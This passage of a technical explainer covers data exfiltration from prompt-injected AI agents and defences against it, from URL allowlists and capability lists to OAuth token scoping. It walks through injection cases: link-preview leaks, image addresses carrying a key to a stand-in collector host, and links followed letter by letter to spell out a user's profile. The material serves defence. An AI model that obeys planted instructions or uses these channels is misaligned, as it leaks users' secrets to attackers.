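Messaging apps create the same problem with link previews. When a message contains a link, an app such as Slack or Telegram may fetch the page to show its title and a small picture. If an injected agent replies with a link that has private data in its query, the preview sends the data to the attacker as soon as the message arrives, without the user clicking. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* found that OpenClaw, a popular agent, was exposed to this attack with its default Telegram settings. Users can turn previews off by adding `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram part of its configuration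 file. Willison (2024) had already described the danger in Slack and passed on Rehberger's advice that a program can turn off previews for the messages it posts.

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork leaked data through email. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* attributes the leak to a rule that let the agent send emails and Teams messages without approval. As Willison explains, even an email to the user's own inbox could leak data, because it could contain images from outside websites, and opening it sent requests to those sites. The image addresses could include links that downloaded files from OneDrive, Microsoft's storage service, without a login. Each link was therefore a bearer token, and one short address could expose a file of any size.

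The planted note could use `post_issue` in the same way, by getting the model to write an issue with an image whose address is on `collector.example` and contains the tracker key. The harness approves the POST request because its host and path are right. If the tracker displays outside images, the key is sent to the contributor when someone first opens the issue. To prevent this, the harness can check every address in the issue's text against a separate list of hosts that the display may contact, and turn images and links to any other host into plain text.

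### Measuring leaks that the user doesn't see

A preview can also bring an attacker's instructions into an assistant's context. Many assistants automatically fetch a page when a user mentions its address, and add its title and description to the context. *Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) tested what happens when the title and description contain instructions to send data elsewhere.

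They used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model, and always asked it to summarize a page. The context also contained a secret. They put instructions in the page's title, description, body text or link text, telling the model to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. The model reached the page either directly or through redirects. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The model sent a request to the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88%. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked harmless. In 120 runs with ordinary pages, the model never contacted that server.

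Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable but harder to notice. The model contacted the server in 238 of 240 runs when it had to send the secret whole, and in 185 of 240 when it had to split it. The first request contained recognizable private data in 97% of the whole-secret runs but only 26% of the split-secret runs. A filter that inspects each request separately would miss many of the pieces.

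Lan and colleagues also tested defences, with 30 runs for each. These are the results for some of them:

| Defence | Runs in which data left |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Marking outside text as untrusted | 100% |
| Telling the model to ignore instructions in web content | 67% |
| Both of these | 57% |
| Allowlist of four domains | 0% |

The allowlist result is less impressive than it looks, because the attacker's server was on `evil-collector.net`, which was not on the list. Cowork's list would have passed the same test. Lan and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could go through a trusted site that redirects elsewhere or has been compromised.

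A filter for random-looking strings also scored 0%, but this result is hard to interpret. The model never tried to send the secret while the filter was on, and Lan and colleagues suggest that it avoided such strings because of the monitoring. But a filter that inspects finished calls shouldn't change what the model writes unless the model receives information about the filter. The filter looked for values with more than 4 bits of entropy (a measure of randomness) per character. The paper's example key, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, has about 3.85, so the filter would have let it through.

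The 88% figure comes from one small model under conditions that favoured the attacker. Lan and colleagues argue that larger models may be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they did not test any. Anthropic reports that on one prompt injection benchmark, single attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time, rising to 5 or 6% when attackers could adapt over 100 attempts. But PromptArmor says its attack on Copilot Cowork had a high success rate against the same model. A low benchmark score is evidence only about the attacks tested, and a product may face others.

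### Judging the exact address

For agents that can't work from a fixed list of sites, OpenAI and Anthropic use rules based on where the exact address came from.

ChatGPT can automatically fetch an address that OpenAI's crawler has already recorded. The crawler is a program that finds public web pages, and it has no access to users' conversations. An address with a user's password in the query would fail this check, because the crawler would never have found it. ChatGPT then either looks for another source or shows the user a warning. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) says that the same mechanism covers the Atlas browser and the Deep Research agent. When the mechanism detects that a request would send information from the conversation to a third party, it either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request.

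OpenAI preferred this to a list of trusted sites partly because trusted sites can redirect to others. It also worried that a strict list would produce so many warnings that people would click through them without reading. The rule covers only data in the address, and OpenAI says a page that passes may still contain harmful instructions. Every part of the product also has to apply the rule. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger recalls that OpenAI's apps for Mac and iPhone at first lacked an earlier version of the check.

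Anthropic lets Claude open pages with its `web_fetch` tool only at exact addresses that the user typed or that Claude's search tool returned. If a planted note tells Claude to add private data to the end of an address, `web_fetch` rejects the altered address.

In July 2026, Willison (2026) described a gap in this rule that Ayush Paul had found. Claude could also open links on pages it had already fetched. Paul built a website for a fake coffee shop that showed Claude special pages with a link for each letter of the alphabet. The pages told Claude to find the user's profile by following the links one letter at a time. The website supplied every address, but the links Claude chose spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem and did not pay Paul a reward. It closed the gap by stopping `web_fetch` from following links on the pages it fetches.

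OpenAI faced a similar attack. *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* describes how the security company Radware gave ChatGPT a set of ready-made addresses, each ending in a single letter or digit, and had it open them in order. OpenAI responded by restricting which links from emails ChatGPT may open, and one test is now whether the link appears in a public index. But an attacker's pages can be in the index too. Rehberger points out that any fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages, enough to represent every letter and digit.

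### How much a choice of address can carry

One bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question, so *k* bits can distinguish 2^*k* possibilities. If an agent chooses among *N* addresses that an attacker can watch, each fetch carries up to log₂ *N* bits, or about 4.7 bits for 26 addresses. A query can hold far more, with 12,000 bits in 2,000 characters if each is chosen from 64 possibilities.

So the rules on exact addresses greatly reduce how much data can leak, but a key is small. Suppose the random part of the tracker key contains 128 bits. (The prefix `trk_live_` adds nothing, because every key has it.) An agent that makes *m* fetches can produce *N*^*m* different sequences. With *N* = 26, the attacker needs 28 fetches for this number to exceed 2¹²⁸, and an agent doing research might make that many without anyone noticing.

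Rehberger suggests preventing the agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, or caching each page for a while so that a second visit sends no request. With 26 fixed addresses, the agent can then visit them all in 26! (26 × 25 × … × 1) different orders, so its choice of order can carry 88.4 bits. The agent can also stop early, which raises the total to 89.8 bits.

About 38 bits of the key are still missing, so the attacker has roughly 300 billion possible keys to try. At 100 guesses a second on the tracker, that would take about a century. But 90 bits are more than enough for a name, since even a random string of six letters needs only 28.

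The protection also depends heavily on the number of addresses:

| Addresses the attacker can watch | Bits per fetch | Fetches needed for a 128-bit key, with repeats | Total bits if each address works once |
|---|---|---|---|
| 26 | 4.7 | 28 | 90 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 25 | 140 |
| 4,096 | 12 | 11 | About 43,000 |

A ban on repeat visits would therefore not protect the key even with the 36 pages in Rehberger's example, and he mentions that an attacker could use thousands. With one indexed page for each of 4,096 common first names, a single fetch would reveal the user's name. The ban would not have helped against Paul's website either, because its nested links led to new addresses after each letter.

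These totals are upper limits, reached only if the model encodes the data perfectly and the requests arrive in order. If the attacker can see which of the 26 pages the agent visited but not the order, the total falls to 26 bits. Each limit applies to one session, however, so a second session could send the rest of the key.

Limiting the number of fetches would reduce the leak proportionally, however many pages the attacker has, but five fetches among 4,096 pages still carry 60 bits. A stronger option is to give the agent a copy of each page saved before the conversation began. The website's owner then sees no requests, so the agent's choice of pages reveals nothing to them. The copy may be out of date, which matters a lot for news but little for a software manual. The company could copy its guide to the release agent's machine each night and remove network access from `read_docs`.

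### Tracking where data came from

Information-flow control labels data by its source, keeps the label attached as the data moves, and checks the label before any data leaves. This check would allow an address on a permitted host if the address came from public text, but not if it came from the tracker key.

Lan and colleagues propose something similar for instructions. The harness would mark text from the web as untrusted, and any tool call influenced by that text would carry the mark. The check doesn't depend on what the data looks like, so even a four-character piece of a secret would look suspicious. However, it is hard to decide what influenced a call. One can follow a value from line to line in an ordinary program, but with a language model, the safe assumption is that everything in the context influenced everything the model writes.

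*Securing MCP-based Agent Workflows* (Ntousakis, 2026) presents SAMOS, a system that makes this assumption for a whole session. SAMOS is a gateway between an agent and its Model Context Protocol tools. A developer or administrator gives each tool two confidentiality labels, one for what it reads and one for the places it writes to. Each label is either high or low. The gateway also labels the session, updates that label after each tool call, and refuses calls that would break the rules.

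Ntousakis tests SAMOS on one known attack. A user asks an agent to handle the issues in a public GitHub project, and one issue contains instructions to read the user's private projects and publish their contents. The agent's GitHub key gives it access to both the public and private projects. Under SAMOS, reading the public issues gives the session a low label. When the agent then tries to open a private project, the gateway blocks the call, so the agent never obtains the private data.

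SAMOS works only if the labels are right, and people have to write them by hand. One GitHub tool can read both public and private projects, so a single label will be wrong for one kind or the other. Ntousakis suggests either splitting the tool into two or having it report the confidentiality of each project it opens. SAMOS also assumes that the tools themselves can be trusted.

Two earlier systems, CaMeL and FIDES, label individual pieces of data. According to Ntousakis, CaMeL enforces its rules with a custom Python interpreter, while FIDES works in the part of the agent that plans tool calls and can keep some tool results out of its memory. Finer labels can permit more requests. For example, if a label shows that `lang=en` came from the user, the harness could allow it in an address even after the agent has read something private. But labelling data so finely is difficult in practice, so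 Ntousakis labels tools instead.

Labels on data can also miss information leaked through the choice of address. Each link on Paul's website was public text from the attacker's own pages, so a check on the address alone would find nothing private in it. The choice of which link to open revealed the private information. To catch this, a system has to label decisions as well as values. A session label covers decisions automatically because it applies to every later call.

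The agent can do less under these rules. Suppose the company labels the output of `run_tests` as high, because a failing test might print the tracker key, and labels `read_docs` as writing to a low destination, because its requests go to a public website. After running the tests, the release agent can't open a page of the guide, even if a test has just failed and the guide explains why. It also can't read the guide before running the tests, because under the rule that stopped the GitHub attack, a session that has read public text can't go on to read private data.

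Ntousakis suggests that an agent in a confidential session could ask a second agent in a separate session to look up public information. The release agent could get its page this way, but to request the right page it has to pass on something from the test output, such as an error code. The second agent might then include that detail in an address. Somebody still has to decide which details may pass between the sessions.

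## Checking every tool call against a list of permissions

A URL scope limits web requests, but agents also read files, edit them and run commands. A harness can control all of these in the same way. It keeps a list of capabilities outside the model's context, and before each tool call it looks for a capability that covers the call. If it finds none, it refuses the call. The model can propose any call, but it can't read or change the list.

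### Capabilities before agents

Computer scientists worked out the main ideas in the 1960s and 1970s. Dennis and Van Horn's *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations* (1966) defined basic operations for computers that run many programs at once, in a design where each process has a list of capabilities. Levy's *Early Capability Architectures* describes how a process could create a subordinate and use the GRANT operation to copy a capability to the subordinate's list, with the access rights the creator specified. An agent that hands part of its task to a sub-agent needs much the same operation.

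Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), described a capability as an "unforgeable ticket". They also argued that a program should have only the privileges its job requires, and that access should rest on "permission rather than exclusion", so that a program can do nothing until someone permits it. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) points out that coding agents usually start from the opposite default. They inherit the user's files, credentials and network access when they are installed, and then read text from strangers.

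### CapScope's three rules

Bouras and colleagues applied these ideas to coding agents in a system called CapScope. They write a capability as Cap[*e*, φ], where *e* is a type of effect and φ is a test on the arguments of a call. The capability covers a call if the tool has effect *e* and the arguments pass φ.

CapScope has three effect types: Read, Write and Exec (running a command). A Write capability for `src/` covers an edit to `src/parser.py` but not to `tests/test_parser.py`. The harness resolves any `..` or symbolic link (a file that points to another file) before it compares paths. It splits a compound command into parts and checks each one, so permission to run `pytest` doesn't cover a second command after a semicolon.

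CapScope has no effect type for web requests. The release agent needs two, here named Fetch and Report, with the URL check as their test:

| Tool | Capability | What passes the test φ |
|---|---|---|
| `read_docs` | Cap[Fetch, φ₁] | GET requests under `https://docs.example.com:443/guide/` |
| `post_issue` | Cap[Report, φ₂] | POST requests under `https://api.tracker.example:443/projects/release/` |
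| `run_tests` | Cap[Exec, φ₃] | Commands that start with `pytest` |

If both web tools had the same effect type, the tracker's capability would also cover a `read_docs` call, so the tools would no longer have separate scopes. The harness has to apply φ₂ to the finished request, because the model's call to `post_issue` contains no address.

Three rules determine how capabilities come into being and what they permit:

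1. **Mint** creates capabilities, using only trusted input. Before the agent reads any file, CapScope gives a language model the user's request and the names of the project's files, and asks which permissions the task will need. Ordinary code checks the answer and turns it into a fixed upper limit for the whole task.
2. **Derive** produces a list for a sub-agent. The agent that delegates the work requests some capabilities, and the harness keeps those that lie within the limit and drops the rest.
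3. **Invoke** runs a tool call if a capability on the calling agent's own list covers it. Otherwise the harness blocks the call and tells the model so.

In the second rule, Cap[*e*, φ′] lies within Cap[*e*, φ] if every argument that passes φ′ also passes φ. No program can decide this for arbitrary tests, so CapScope stores each scope as simple data, such as the start of a path, which the harness can compare. The harness can compare URL scopes the same way. A scope for `/guide/install/` lies within one for `/guide/` if the scheme, host, port and method match.

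Invoke never adds a capability, and Derive never goes beyond the existing limit, so every permission an agent uses must trace back to Mint. A planted note can change the model's requests but not the limit, which is already set by then. CapScope can also let a user approve one more capability during a task, which counts as a new Mint, but the model can't approve its own request.

In Hardy's remedy for the confused deputy, the program chooses a capability for each write. In CapScope, the model still writes an ordinary name, and the harness accepts the call if any permission on the list covers it. An agent can therefore still use a permission for a purpose other than the one it was granted for.

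### Separate lists for sub-agents

Dividing the work among several agents reduces this problem if each agent has its own list of permissions. Suppose a coding agent has to repair a failing test, which requires permission to edit source code, and the test's output contains the fake notice about a changed signing key. If all the sub-agents share one list, the one that runs the tests can also edit source code, so it can insert the attacker's key. CapScope gives the test runner permission to read and run tests, and gives permission to edit to a separate "patcher". The test runner may still try to follow the notice, but the harness blocks its edit.

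The release agent could similarly use a reader with the Fetch capability, a tester with Exec and a reporter with Report. The reader would see the planted note but not the test output. The tester might see the tracker key but would have no tool that sends web requests. The company would still have to block the tests' own network access.

### Testing CapScope

Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They planted instructions to run a harmless-looking utility or write to a project file, neither of which was needed to fix the bug. The instructions appeared in the README file, an `AGENTS.md` file of instructions for agents, a skill file (a reusable set of instructions), a comment in the source code, or the test output.

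The experiment compared CapScope with three alternatives. The first had no restrictions. The second blocked familiar dangers, such as `sudo`, `curl` and files that usually contain secrets. The third used a list of permissions written for the task, but gave every agent the same list. In all four setups, an orchestrator delegated work to a runner, a patcher and a verifier. Each combination was tried three times, for a total of 300 runs, or 75 per setup.

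| Permissions | Planted action ran | Repair succeeded | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 seconds |
| Fixed list of dangers | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 seconds |
| Shared list for the task | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 seconds |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 seconds |

The fixed list of dangers made almost no difference, because the planted actions were ordinary project work. CapScope did not improve the model's judgment either, as the model proposed the planted action in 34 of the 75 CapScope runs. The harness blocked it in nearly all of those 34.

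All three successful attacks on CapScope came through `AGENTS.md`, which the harness loads automatically. Bouras and colleagues give two causes. Some permissions were broader than the subtask required, such as write access to a whole directory instead of one file. In other cases, the planted text influenced how the orchestrator described a subtask, so the sub-agent received the permission the attacker wanted. Each time, the task's overall limit allowed the action, and the check on the call could not stop it.

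CapScope failed to complete seven repairs. In two, the model that predicted the permissions had left out the one for editing the source code. In two others, the runner found the right fix but wasn't allowed to make it, and the orchestrator didn't pass it to the patcher. The last three had passing tests but ran out of time.

Much of the extra time probably came from the model retrying after refusals. In 27 of the 34 runs where it proposed the planted action, it tried more than once. Five runs reached the 15-minute limit, which raised the mean; the median was 208 seconds. A person watching the agent could have stopped the repeated attempts, but the experiment allowed no human approval.

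The gap between 33 and 3 is large enough to take seriously, but it comes from one model, qwen3.5-flash, on five tiny repairs. A long refactoring job would need many more permissions, and a model predicting them from file names would probably miss more.

CapScope also does not keep data confidential. An agent with permission to read one file and write to another can copy a secret between them. Commands such as `grep` and `find` can look at files outside the agent's Read scope because CapScope allows them by default. The release agent's tester could include the tracker key in its report to the orchestrator, which might pass the key to the reporter to include in a public issue. The Report capability would allow that request because its test checks the address, not the text. To prevent this, the company would need to control how information flows between the agents.

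### What agent frameworks check by default

In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) examined the public code of two frameworks for building agents, LangChain/LangGraph and LlamaIndex, and of the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to Stripe's payment service. All three let the developer choose which tools or actions to offer the agent, but by default none checks whether the agent is allowed to use the particular values in a call.

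Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed piece of model output that changed a merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain carried out the change on a simulated payment system. The account number had the right format, and no rule specified which accounts were acceptable. A similar test worked on LlamaIndex. Likewise, a framework that checks only that the argument to `read_docs` is text would accept an address on `collector.example`.

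These are design choices, and Mellafe Zuvic does not call them security bugs. Developers can add their own checks or require human approval. Stripe also lets a merchant restrict what an API key can do, and the audit did not cover Stripe's servers. But a developer who assumes that choosing an agent's tools also limits how the agent can use them will leave that use unchecked.

Mellafe Zuvic's own control, ScopeGate, refuses a call unless it passes all of these checks:

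- The tool is on the list.
- Each restricted argument has a permitted value.
- Any amount of money is a finite number between zero and a set maximum.
- A call that must not run twice comes with a trusted idempotency key, a label that lets the service recognize a repeat.

An early version had a bug that allowed a payment whose amount was NaN, which means "not a number". Every greater-than or less-than comparison with NaN is false, so a rule that refuses amounts greater than the maximum never applies to it. The corrected version requires the amount to be within the range, and NaN fails that test. An error during the check also leads to a refusal.

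ScopeGate refused all 48 prepared attacks and all 29 unauthorized calls from a model that could see why its earlier attempts had failed. It allowed all 10 legitimate calls in a separate test. However, Mellafe Zuvic wrote both ScopeGate and the tests, and a list with one permitted account is an easy case.

AgentDojo, a larger test, supports the main point about arguments. Its agents do banking, travel and office tasks while exposed to planted text meant to divert them. In one task, the agent has to raise a standing order for rent after reading the landlord's notice. The planted instructions are to use the same tool to redirect a different standing order to the attacker. A list of tool names can't permit the first call and refuse the second, because the calls differ only in their arguments.

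*Ajar* (Sharma, Lin and colleagues, 2026) checked how many of AgentDojo's attacks each kind of list would permit. A list of the tool names that each task required permitted 99 of 609 attacks. A list of exact arguments, based on the benchmark's own solutions, permitted one. Real users have no such solutions, so the second figure shows what a nearly perfect list could achieve.

### Hiding a tool or refusing a call

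A harness can also leave a tool out of the descriptions it sends to the model. *Beyond Static Sandboxing* (Sidik and Rokach, 2026) reports that OpenClaw offers at least 15 tools in every session, although summarizing a document may take only one. The paper's system, AgentWarden, guesses the type of task from the user's first message and describes only suitable tools to the model. It also checks each call before the call runs.

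AgentWarden blocked every attempt to run a shell command in a test of 500 tasks, but on AgentDojo it only reduced the success rate of attacks from 90.3% to 88.9%. A likely reason is that many of the AgentDojo attacks used tools that the tasks also needed, such as the one for sending money, and that AgentWarden's rules mostly targeted other dangers. Sidik and Rokach instead explain that these attacks arrive in the results of tools, whereas AgentWarden controls calls. This is less likely to be the reason, because the attacks still need a tool call to do any harm.

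Hiding has a different benefit, which *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) measured with a system called PORTICO. PORTICO gives an agent a temporary permission for part of a task, such as editing one extra file. When that part ends, PORTICO removes the permission from the options the model sees and rejects any later attempt to use it. It rejected all ten such attempts in tests, while an otherwise identical system without the expiry rule allowed them all.

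Santos-Grueiro then let the model see more options without changing which calls could run. In this small test of four episodes, no forbidden action ran, but blocked proposals rose from 67 to 84. This suggests that hiding options reduces wasted attempts, which might have helped with CapScope's long running times, while refusing forbidden calls provides the security. A model can still learn a hidden tool's name from a document or an earlier message, so the harness has to refuse the call even if the tool isn't in the current descriptions.

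### Capabilities checked by a compiler

CapScope and ScopeGate check each call as the agent makes it. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a system, TACIT, that does part of the check earlier. The agent writes a short Scala 3 program instead of making separate tool calls. The compiler works out which capabilities each part of the program could use. If a part could use one it shouldn't have, the compiler rejects the program before any of it runs.

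For example, the function `requestNetwork` gives one block of code access to a list of hosts. The compiler prevents the code from saving this access and using it after the block ends. Some checks still have to wait until the program runs. TACIT needs the actual path to check whether a file is in the permitted directory.

The compiler can also protect secrets in a way that CapScope can't. TACIT wraps secret data in a type called `Classified`. The agent's program can process the contents only with functions that have no access to files, the network or anything else outside the calculation, and the result stays wrapped. If the tracker key were wrapped this way, the release agent could check that it started with `trk_live_`, but the compiler would reject code that sent the key anywhere. If the agent printed the key, the model would receive only `Classified(****)`.

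Odersky and colleagues tested two models on 131 trials each, including some with planted instructions and some in which users asked for secrets directly. When TACIT wrapped the secrets, none reached the agent's output. Without the wrapping, Claude Sonnet 4.6 kept secrets out of its output in 98.5% of trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 91.6%. MiniMax revealed secrets in 8 of the 11 trials in which the user asked for them.

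Writing Scala did not make the agents perform much worse. On simulated customer service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. On a set of software repairs, MiniMax's success rate fell slightly, from 43.3% to 41.7%.

The compiler's guarantee ends when the agent starts an outside program such as `pytest`, so `run_tests` would still need a sandbox. Odersky and colleagues expect the compiler to enforce limits on sub-agents too, but leave a full test to future work.

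*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) covers sub-agents. Its system uses Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. Each tool needs a capability token to act, and the token for web requests lists the permitted hosts. The paper proves that an agent can't create a sub-agent with more authority than its own. The proofs cover individual checks, not the complete system, and they don't guarantee that the permissions are sensible. For example, an agent with permission to read a key and publish a file can still publish the key.

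### Who writes the list

Each of these systems enforces a list that a person or model has to write. An attacker can use the extra permissions if the list is too broad, and the agent can't finish its work if it is too narrow. CapScope's experiment had both kinds of failure.

Mellafe Zuvic argues that no part of the list should come from a model, even indirectly, because whatever corrupts the model's calls could also corrupt its rules. CapScope does use a model for this, but only before the agent has read any outside text other than file names. This protects well against instructions planted in files, but less well against a hidden flaw from the model's training, which could also affect the list. However, a person can't write a new list for every request to a general-purpose assistant.

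Models also make ordinary mistakes when they write rules. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) tested a model that wrote access rules in a single attempt, and found that 62.5% of the rules meant to deny access were wrong. The model also tended to leave out conditions. For example, it turned permission for "the assigned nurse" into permission for every nurse. Such a rule can run without an error, so someone has to check its meaning.

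*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) lets a model revise the list as the agent learns more about its task. A separate program, called a solver, compares the old and new lists. If the new list permits nothing that the old one refused, Progent applies it automatically. Any change that adds a permission needs approval. In the paper's AgentDojo tests, only 6% of changes needed approval.

Progent reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%. In that test, Shi and colleagues approved every added permission automatically to represent a careless user, so the solver's guarantee provided little protection. Most of the protection must have come from the model that wrote the list, which rarely added permissions the attacker wanted. When a person reviewed the initial list and every addition, no attacks succeeded.

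Sharma and colleagues tested Progent and four other systems by offering them calls that an agent might make, including many that it never made in practice. This reveals excess permissions even if no attack happens to use them. They gave more weight to dangerous calls, so an unnecessary payment to a stranger counted 27 times as much as an unnecessary read. These are the results with Claude Sonnet 5 making the decisions or writing the rules:

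| System | Unnecessary calls allowed, weighted by harm | Necessary calls allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Permission Assistant | 8.1% | 96.1% |
| CaMeL | 9.0% | 70.0% |
| Progent | 10.3% | 90.2% |
| AC4A | 11.1% | 71.5% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 30.1% | Not measured |

For comparison, a list of tool names scored 35.5% on the first measure, and a list of exact arguments scored 0.2%. CaMeL and Permission Assistant allowed similar amounts of unnecessary access, but CaMeL refused far more of the calls that the tasks required. A system can have a low rate of successful attacks and still have both problems. In the rent task, for instance, Progent would also have let the agent set the payment to zero.

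Excess permissions matter even without an attacker. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (2026) cites a test of 11 agents in which six chose a more powerful tool than necessary in over 30% of cases.

Agents commonly ask the user about uncertain cases, but people approve most requests. The same paper cites one company's report that users of its coding agent approved 93% of permission prompts. Yan (2026), in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, tested whether people do better if they set rules in advance. The 113 participants, none of them software professionals, supervised a simulated agent that took 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the user's request. One group decided whether to approve each action, another relied on a model to review them, and the third wrote "allow", "ask" or "never" rules for spending money, sending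 information, deleting things and reading private data.

The group that wrote rules blocked 20.1 percentage points fewer of the unwanted actions than the group that approved each action, and 14.5 points fewer than automatic review. Participants chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which put off most of the decisions. In this group, 148 unwanted actions went ahead, and participants had approved 133 of them when asked. The categories were broad, and people who know a system well might write better rules, but the result is still a reason to be wary of "ask" as the default.

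The release agent does the same job for every release, so its developers can write the three capabilities by hand and have the harness refuse everything else. They can review the refused calls after each run and add a permission if the agent needs it. That way, nobody has to judge an unfamiliar address while a release is waiting.

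## What OAuth access tokens restrict

The capability list in the harness has no effect on the tracker's server, which accepts a copied tracker key from any computer. OAuth, the usual way for an agent to act on a user's account, attaches limits to the credential so that the service can enforce them.

Suppose the tracker's owner stops issuing permanent keys and offers `post_issue` as a tool on its own server, `mcp.tracker.example`. The release agent now needs an OAuth access token to use the tool.

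### Who issues, presents and checks a token

With OAuth, a user can give a program access to an account without giving it the password, as *Overlaying Governance* (2026) explains. There are four roles:

| Role | What it does | In the example |
|---|---|---|
| Resource owner | Approves the access | The company's release manager |
| Client | Requests the token and presents it | The harness |
| Authorization server | Issues the token | `auth.tracker.example` |
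| Resource server | Checks the token and carries out the request | `mcp.tracker.example` |

The harness gets and uses a token like this:

1. It generates a random secret, called a verifier, and computes a hash of it.
2. It opens the authorization server's page in the release manager's browser, sending the hash and a description of the access it wants.
3. The release manager logs in and approves. The authorization server sends the browser back to the harness with a temporary code.
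4. The harness sends the code and the verifier to the authorization server, which checks the verifier against the hash and issues an access token.
5. The harness includes the token in its requests to the tracker's server.

The verifier is part of a method called PKCE. Someone who intercepts the code in step 3 can't exchange it for a token without the verifier. None of these steps involves the model.

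The token gives the harness no more permissions on the tracker than the release manager has. According to *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025), OAuth was designed for a program acting for one person, which causes problems when an agent serves a group. For example, if a finance chief's agent answers questions in a shared chat, it can look up and post salaries that the other members aren't allowed to see.

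### The fields that narrow a token

An access token is often a set of named fields with the authorization server's signature, which lets the resource server detect any change. The release agent's token might contain:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.tracker.example",
  "sub": "release-manager",
  "aud": "https://mcp.tracker.example/mcp",
  "scope": "issues:write",
  "exp": 1796468400
}
```

The first two fields identify the issuer and the user. The other three set limits.

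`scope` gives the type of access. The tracker's owner chooses the scope names and decides what each one permits.

`exp` is the expiry time, in seconds since the start of 1970. Here it is 11:00 UTC on 5 December 2026. Access tokens often last about an hour. The client may also receive a refresh token, which it can exchange for new access tokens, so a short expiry gives little protection if the refresh token leaks too.

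The `aud` (audience) claim identifies the server that should accept the token. Without this limit, a malicious service that received a token could use it to act as the user on another service.

The authorization server can set the audience only if it knows where the client plans to use the token. The client supplies this in the `resource` parameter, which Campbell, Bradley and Tschofenig define in *Resource Indicators for OAuth 2.0* (RFC 8707). They say that the server "should" restrict the token to that resource, which is weaker than "must". *Resource Token Response Parameter* (2025), a draft standard, points out that the server also doesn't have to tell the client which resource the token covers.

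A client can name several resources at once, but this is risky. A client that requests the scopes `calendar` and `contacts` for two servers is asking for both scopes on both servers. Each server could also use the token it receives to access the other. Campbell and colleagues therefore encourage clients to name one resource per token. Where many customers share a host, they recommend that the resource name include the path that identifies the customer.

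The scope `issues:write` doesn't specify a project. In *OAuth 2.0 Rich Authorization Requests*, or RFC 9396, Lodderstedt, Richer and Campbell define `authorization_details`, a field for more precise permissions. The tracker could support an entry like this:

```json
{
  "type": "tracker_issue",
  "locations": ["https://mcp.tracker.example/mcp"],
  "actions": ["create"],
  "identifier": "release"
}
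```

The `type` field determines how the authorization server interprets the other fields in an entry, and the server must refuse types or fields it doesn't recognize. Listing several values in one entry can permit more than the user intended, as can separate lists of methods and hosts in a URL scope. An entry with the actions "read" and "write" and the data types "contacts" and "photos" permits all four combinations. The client has to send two entries to permit only reading contacts and writing photos.

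No general rule determines whether one entry permits less than another, because each service defines its own fields. For example, "write" may include "read" in one service but not in another. The authorization server therefore needs separate comparison code for each type.

### Proof of possession

A thief who copies the token can still use it on the server it is meant for until it expires. *OAuth 2.0 Demonstrating Proof of Possession (DPoP)* (RFC 9449), by Fett, Campbell and colleagues, defines DPoP, which prevents this by binding the token to a pair of cryptographic keys. The client keeps the private key and signs with it, and anyone can check the signatures with the public key.

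When the harness requests a token, it also sends its public key and a signature made with the private key. The authorization server links the token to that public key. For each later request, the harness signs a new proof containing:

- the request's method and its address, without the query
- the time
- a unique identifier, such as 96 random bits
- a hash of the access token, base64url(SHA-256(token))
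- a number chosen by the server, if the server requires one

The tracker's server checks that the signature is valid, the key is the one linked to the token, the time is recent, and the method, address and hash match the request. If a failing test prints the token and the model sends it to `collector.example`, the contributor can't use it without the private key.

This protection depends on where the private key is stored. If the harness keeps the token and the key in environment variables that the tests inherit, a test can print both. Even if the operating system prevents the key from being exported, hostile code inside the client can still use it to sign proofs. Fett and colleagues warn that such code could also create proofs with future timestamps and send them out with the token. The server can prevent this by requiring each proof to include an unpredictable value that the server issued.

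The DPoP proof doesn't cover the body of the request, which contains the issue, so DPoP relies on the encrypted connection to protect the body. The proof also doesn't help when a planted note causes the model to call `post_issue`, because the harness will sign a valid proof for that call. Surapani and colleagues likewise point out that having a key doesn't show that the model chose the tool for an authorized purpose.

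### What the Model Context Protocol requires

The tracker's server uses the Model Context Protocol (MCP). Developers download its software kits more than 400 million times a month, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026). The protocol's first version, from November 2024, did not require authentication. Revisions added OAuth in March 2025 and audience checks in June 2025. The 28 July 2026 revision made six changes to authorization, which *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) describes as clarifications of established OAuth practice.

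In MCP's terms, the harness contains an MCP client, and the tracker runs an MCP server. The Model Context Protocol's official authorization text sets these rules for systems that follow it:

- The client must name the MCP server in the `resource` parameter, even if the authorization server ignores it.
- The client must send the access token in the `Authorization` header of every request, and never in the query of an address.
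- The MCP server must check that the token is valid and that the authorization server issued it for that MCP server.
- The MCP server must not accept any other token or pass one on.

The client must also use PKCE, and must stop if the authorization server doesn't support it. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* states that the `resource` parameter limits a token only when the authorization server supports the parameter.

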